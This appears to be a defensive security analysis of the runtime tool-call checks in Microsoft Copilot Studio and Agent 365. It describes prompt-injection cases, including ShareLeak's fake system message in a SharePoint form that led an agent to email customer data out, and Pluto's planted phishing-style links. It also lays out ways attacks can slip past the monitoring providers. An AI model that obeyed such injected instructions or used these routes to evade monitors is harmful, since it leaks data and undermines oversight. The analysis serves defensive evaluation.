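Agent 365 has a separate real-time check that is easy to confuse with external threat detection because Defender makes the decision in both. It covers tool calls that pass through the Agent 365 tooling gateway, a common route between agents and their tools. The check also relies on webhooks, and Microsoft (2026) announced it as a preview.

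The two checks cover different tool calls. Copilot Studio's check starts when a Copilot Studio agent's orchestrator chooses a tool. Trent explains in *Runtime Protection for Agents* that the gateway check applies to two groups of tools that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of connecting agents to outside tools. These are Work IQ, Microsoft's tools for working with Microsoft 365 data such as email and calendars, and tools that an organisation has registered with Agent 365.

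The gateway check also evaluates what a tool returns, so it may stop hostile instructions there before the agent acts on them. Customers also have more control over this check. By default, Defender records suspicious actions but lets them proceed. To block them, an administrator creates a rule and chooses which agents it covers and which threats to block, such as leaked passwords or messages to untrusted domains. These are the rules that stopped blocking on 1 July until administrators recreated them.

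A Copilot Studio agent that uses a Work IQ tool might go through both checks, but one that sends email through an ordinary connector outside the gateway goes through only the Copilot Studio check. Blocking rules that a company has set up in Agent 365 may therefore not cover its Copilot Studio agents. Trent also warns that the gateway does not protect agents that rely on unsupported tools.

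## What can the check miss?

A provider can only judge what Copilot Studio sends it, so it will miss some harmful actions however good it is. Other harmful actions are sent to the provider but look like ordinary work. A stricter provider will catch more of these, but it will also interrupt more legitimate tasks.

### What never reaches the provider

Some gaps come from configuration. Microsoft doesn't run the check for classic agents. The connection to a provider is also off by default, according to *Microsoft Copilot Studio Agent Security Risks*, a rating of the product by the security firm Adversa AI.

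The provider also can't check a tool's output before it reaches the orchestrator, because Copilot Studio contacts the provider only before a tool runs. If an agent opens a document that contains hidden instructions, the orchestrator receives them unchecked. This usually does no harm by itself, because the instructions still have to make the agent do something. If they lead to another tool call, such as sending an email, the request to the provider can include the document's text among the earlier outputs, and the provider has a chance to block the call. A provider that ignores earlier outputs, as CrowdStrike does, has to rely on the later call's inputs.

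The provider gets no further chance to block the agent if no other tool call follows. Microsoft documents a check before each tool call but none on the agent's written reply. This suggests that an agent could retrieve confidential data with one approved call and include it in its answer without contacting the provider again, although Microsoft doesn't say so. The risk is greatest for a public chatbot, where the attacker is the person reading the answer. An attacker who hides instructions in an email usually needs the agent to make another call to send the data out.

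The provider can stop a leak of this kind only at the call that fetches the data, before it knows what the call will return. A filter on the finished reply would help. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) tested nine defence configurations against an automated attacker that revised its attempts over hundreds of rounds. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed, while a check in ordinary program code on the model's replies let nothing through in 15,000 attacks. A filter in a real company would probably do worse, because the test used embedded secrets, and a program can search for a known secret more easily than it can recognise any customer's private details. Copilot Studio has a moderation setting for replies, but according to *Control 1.8*, the governance guide for financial firms, it screens for hate, sexual content,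 violence and self-harm, which do not cover confidential data.

A reply can also do harm without containing any secrets. The security firm Pluto planted web addresses in the response from an outside web service, in the instructions of a connected sub-agent and in the description of an MCP tool. The built-in defences reliably caught overt commands, but when Pluto presented the same address as ordinary product information, the agent passed it on to the user as a clickable link without showing its source. An attacker could use such a link to lead people to a fake sign-in page. Pluto didn't connect an external provider, but a provider would probably have had no chance to block the link, because displaying one doesn't require a tool call.

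Pluto found that Copilot Studio fetches tool descriptions from an MCP server at the start of each chat session, so whoever runs the server can change them after the agent's maker has reviewed them. The orchestrator keeps these descriptions as background for the whole session, but the request to the provider contains only the definition of the chosen tool. A hostile description of one tool could therefore influence a call to another, and the provider would not see that description.

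A single tool call can also start a long series of actions. With Copilot Studio's Computer Use tool, a model operates a web browser by taking screenshots and acting on what they show. One of Pluto's test sessions lasted about two minutes and left eight screenshots. Microsoft describes a check when the orchestrator chooses a tool but doesn't mention one for each click, so the provider probably sees the task given to the model but not what the model then does on the page.

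### Harm that looks like ordinary work

The travel agent in Tenable's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Security Risk* (2025) set a trip's price to $0 with a tool it was supposed to use for changing customers' bookings. Zero is a valid number, so a provider would need a rule about prices, or some knowledge of what the trip should cost, to detect a problem with the call.

The request to the provider may also contain the attacker's words, in the chat messages, the earlier outputs or the orchestrator's stated reason. If the provider uses a language model to judge the request, those words could mislead the model as they misled the orchestrator. For example, an attacker might write in a document that the finance department has already approved the recipient. A fixed rule avoids this problem, but an attacker can still satisfy it. The recipient rule, for instance, accepts any address that appears in a document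 the agent has read.

Attackers can also revise an attempt that fails. *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) found that attackers who adapted got past every detector tested, even several combined, although detectors still stopped some unsophisticated attacks. *PromptArmor* (2025) reports that the detector it introduces had consistently low rates of missed attacks and false alarms, even against attacks automatically optimised to defeat it. But the detector's own developers ran this test, using one attack method, so it is weaker evidence than a test by outsiders. Neither paper is about Copilot Studio's providers.

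An attacker using the chat can learn which attempts fail, because Copilot Studio tells the user when it has blocked a message. Someone attacking the invoice agent by email gets no such notice and has to guess from the lack of a reply. Repeated attempts are also risky for the attacker, because a run of blocked calls should stand out to a security team that is watching for them.

An attacker can also avoid detection by spreading the harm over several steps. *Microsoft patched a Copilot Studio prompt injection. The data exfiltrated anyway* (2026), a VentureBeat article about research by the security firm Capsule Security, describes attacks that split their instructions across several harmless-looking messages. Harmful tool calls can similarly be split into steps that employees request every day. For example, an agent could look up a customer, copy the details into a shared document and later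 give an outsider access to the document.

A provider can defend against this by considering the calls together. Microsoft includes a conversation ID in every request, which a provider can use to keep its own record of what the agent has done so far. It could then detect that the document in the last step contains the customer details from the first. This is harder if the attacker starts a new chat for each step. In Pluto's tests of a public demonstration website, each browser session received its own conversation ID, so a provider would have to link the steps another way, such as through the customer record involved.

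Elia Zaitsev, CrowdStrike's chief technology officer, told VentureBeat that analysing an agent's intent "will sometimes work" but "cannot always work". He prefers to observe what the agent did. That approach has limited use here, because the provider must answer before the tool runs and can observe only the agent's earlier actions.

### How small error rates add up

An agent may make many calls in one task, so even a reliable provider can fail to check a call in a noticeable share of tasks. Suppose that 2% of checks time out, independently of one another, and that the system fails open, so those calls go ahead. In a task with ten calls, the chance that at least one goes ahead unchecked is 1 − 0.98^10, or about 18%. Most unchecked calls will be harmless, but an attacker's call might be among them.

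False alarms add up in the same way. If the provider wrongly blocks 1% of harmless calls, a harmless ten-call task has a 0.99¹⁰, or about 90%, chance of finishing. A company that runs 1,000 such tasks a day would have almost 100 wrongly interrupted. Both error rates are invented for illustration.

Real timeouts probably come in clusters, because an overloaded provider will be slow for many agents at once. At the same average rate, clustered timeouts affect fewer tasks, but an affected task may lose most of its checks.

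### Failing open or failing closed

If the system fails closed, it blocks the 2% of calls whose checks time out instead of letting them through, which stops 18% of ten-call tasks. Timeouts and false alarms together would prevent about 26% of harmless tasks from finishing.

Failing open keeps agents working during a provider outage, but it leaves every agent in the environment with only the built-in filters. It also gives attackers a reason to slow the provider down, perhaps with very long messages that take more time to analyse. This risk is theoretical, and its severity would depend on the provider. Failing closed removes that incentive, but a provider outage then stops the agents too.

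*Control 1.8* advises financial firms to fail open for personal productivity agents and to fail closed for team and enterprise-wide agents. What an agent can do seems at least as important as who uses it. A widely used agent that only answers questions about office opening hours can safely fail open, but a personal agent that can email confidential files perhaps should not. Administrators set the error behaviour for a whole environment, so agents that need different settings must be in separate environments.

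### No way to ask a person

A provider that is unsure about a call still has to allow or block it. *Control 1.8* lists "warn" as a third possible answer, but Microsoft's specification doesn't include it. Asking the user would often resolve the doubt. In the Bcc example, an employee could probably say immediately whether the unexplained address belonged to the company's sales archive.

Capsule found a similar weakness in Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents. Salesforce responded by requiring human confirmation by default when an agent acts through email, according to the news site Claw Times. Naor Paz, Capsule's chief executive, had objected to human confirmation, telling VentureBeat that if a person must approve every operation, "it's just a human clicking through the agent's actions". His objection is weaker against a system that asks a person only about doubtful calls, but a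 Copilot Studio provider cannot do that.

Makers can build an approval step into the agent, as Adversa AI recommends for actions that change outside systems. But the maker must decide in advance which actions need approval, so a provider that is unsure about a particular call cannot trigger the step. The step is also of limited use for agents that run overnight, when nobody is available to approve actions.

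### Delay and data sharing

The waits before each tool call can add up to several seconds, although Microsoft says in its announcement that an agent continues "without delay or disruption" if the provider finds its action safe. The added time would annoy someone in a chat but would hardly matter when an agent processes invoices overnight.

The time limit also restricts how a provider can decide. A large language model may need more than a second to analyze a long conversation, and a human reviewer would. Capsule's product uses small language models trained for the task, which are generally faster, but VentureBeat gives no figures for their speed or accuracy.

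For some organisations, the loss of privacy will be a more serious problem. Microsoft doesn't let customers limit the data that Copilot Studio shares with the provider, which can include the results of earlier tool calls that have little to do with the call under review. Suppose a human-resources agent looks up an employee's sick leave and then books a meeting. The request to approve the meeting may also include the sick-leave record. This happens even if the provider's method doesn't use earlier results, so a customer can share all this data without getting the full benefit in detection.

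*Control 1.8* suggests questions to ask an outside provider before connecting it, including whether it stores conversations, where it hosts its service and how it handles security incidents. An organisation that isn't satisfied with the answers can put its most sensitive agents in a separate environment with an in-house provider.

### ShareLeak

Capsule Security found a flaw in Copilot Studio on 24 November 2025 and named it ShareLeak (CVE-2026-21520). Microsoft confirmed it on 5 December and fixed it on 15 January 2026, according to VentureBeat. Capsule published its findings on 15 April, the day it announced $7 million in funding.

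An attacker entered text that imitated a system message into the comment field of a public SharePoint form, and Copilot Studio combined it with the agent's own instructions. In Capsule's demonstration, the agent then searched connected SharePoint lists for customer data and emailed it to the attacker through Outlook. Microsoft's safety mechanisms flagged the request as suspicious, but the agent still sent the data. A separate data loss prevention system wasn't triggered because the agent had used an authorised Outlook action.

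MITRE's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the public record that Microsoft wrote for the flaw, gives it a severity of 7.5 out of 10 and indicates that an official fix exists. Microsoft published the record on 22 January, and two days later the US cybersecurity agency CISA added an assessment that listed no known exploitation. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) explains that Microsoft made the fix in its own service, so customers didn't have to do anything.

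Claw Times claims that the fix "did not fully prevent data exfiltration", citing VentureBeat and CSO Online, but neither supports the claim. Both report that data leaked during Capsule's tests despite a warning from Microsoft's safety mechanisms, and neither says that Capsule repeated the tests after the fix. VentureBeat's headline mentions the patch before the leak, which may explain the misunderstanding. There is no good evidence that the fix failed, but no one has published an independent retest confirming that it worked. Even a working fix for this form of the attack would not rule out prompt injection through other kinds of content.

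None of these accounts mentions an external provider connected to the agent, so ShareLeak is evidence only about the built-in filters. VentureBeat says a product like Capsule's would block such a leak by checking the tool call, but it reports no test of this, and Capsule has a commercial interest in the claim. The check would cover this attack, because the data left through an email tool. A provider should have received the recipient's address before the agent sent the email, and a rule against emailing outsiders would have stopped it.

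### The lack of independent tests

As of October 2026, nobody appears to have published independent detection or false-alarm rates for external threat detection with any provider. Microsoft illustrates Defender with three constructed scenarios but gives no rates. Miller (2025) describes the feature and its licensing in *Defender for Cloud Apps Helps Protect Copilot Studio Agents* but doesn't test it. Adversa AI bases its rating on Microsoft's documentation and earlier security research. Its score of one out of three for Copilot Studio's input defences, largely due to ShareLeak, doesn't measure how well any provider detects attacks. Pluto ran its own tests, but only of the built-in defences.

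Microsoft suggests that customers use the audit logs to evaluate their provider. Reviewing the blocked calls can help a customer find false alarms. The logs are much less useful for finding missed attacks, because a call that the provider wrongly allowed looks the same in the log as one that it rightly allowed. The record of blocks may also be incomplete. *Control 1.8* warns that blocked prompts don't consistently appear in Defender's advanced search tool, and says that Microsoft has acknowledged the problem and is reviewing it.

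Researchers have run more demanding tests on other kinds of agents. *BrowseSafe++* (2026), a benchmark for agents that browse the web, reports false-positive rates for injection detectors. It also includes attacks that are revised after each failure, with one program working out why the agent resisted and another rewriting the attack. A comparable test of Copilot Studio would give the same attacks and harmless tasks to agents connected to different providers, then count how many attacks succeeded and how many harmless tasks the providers blocked.
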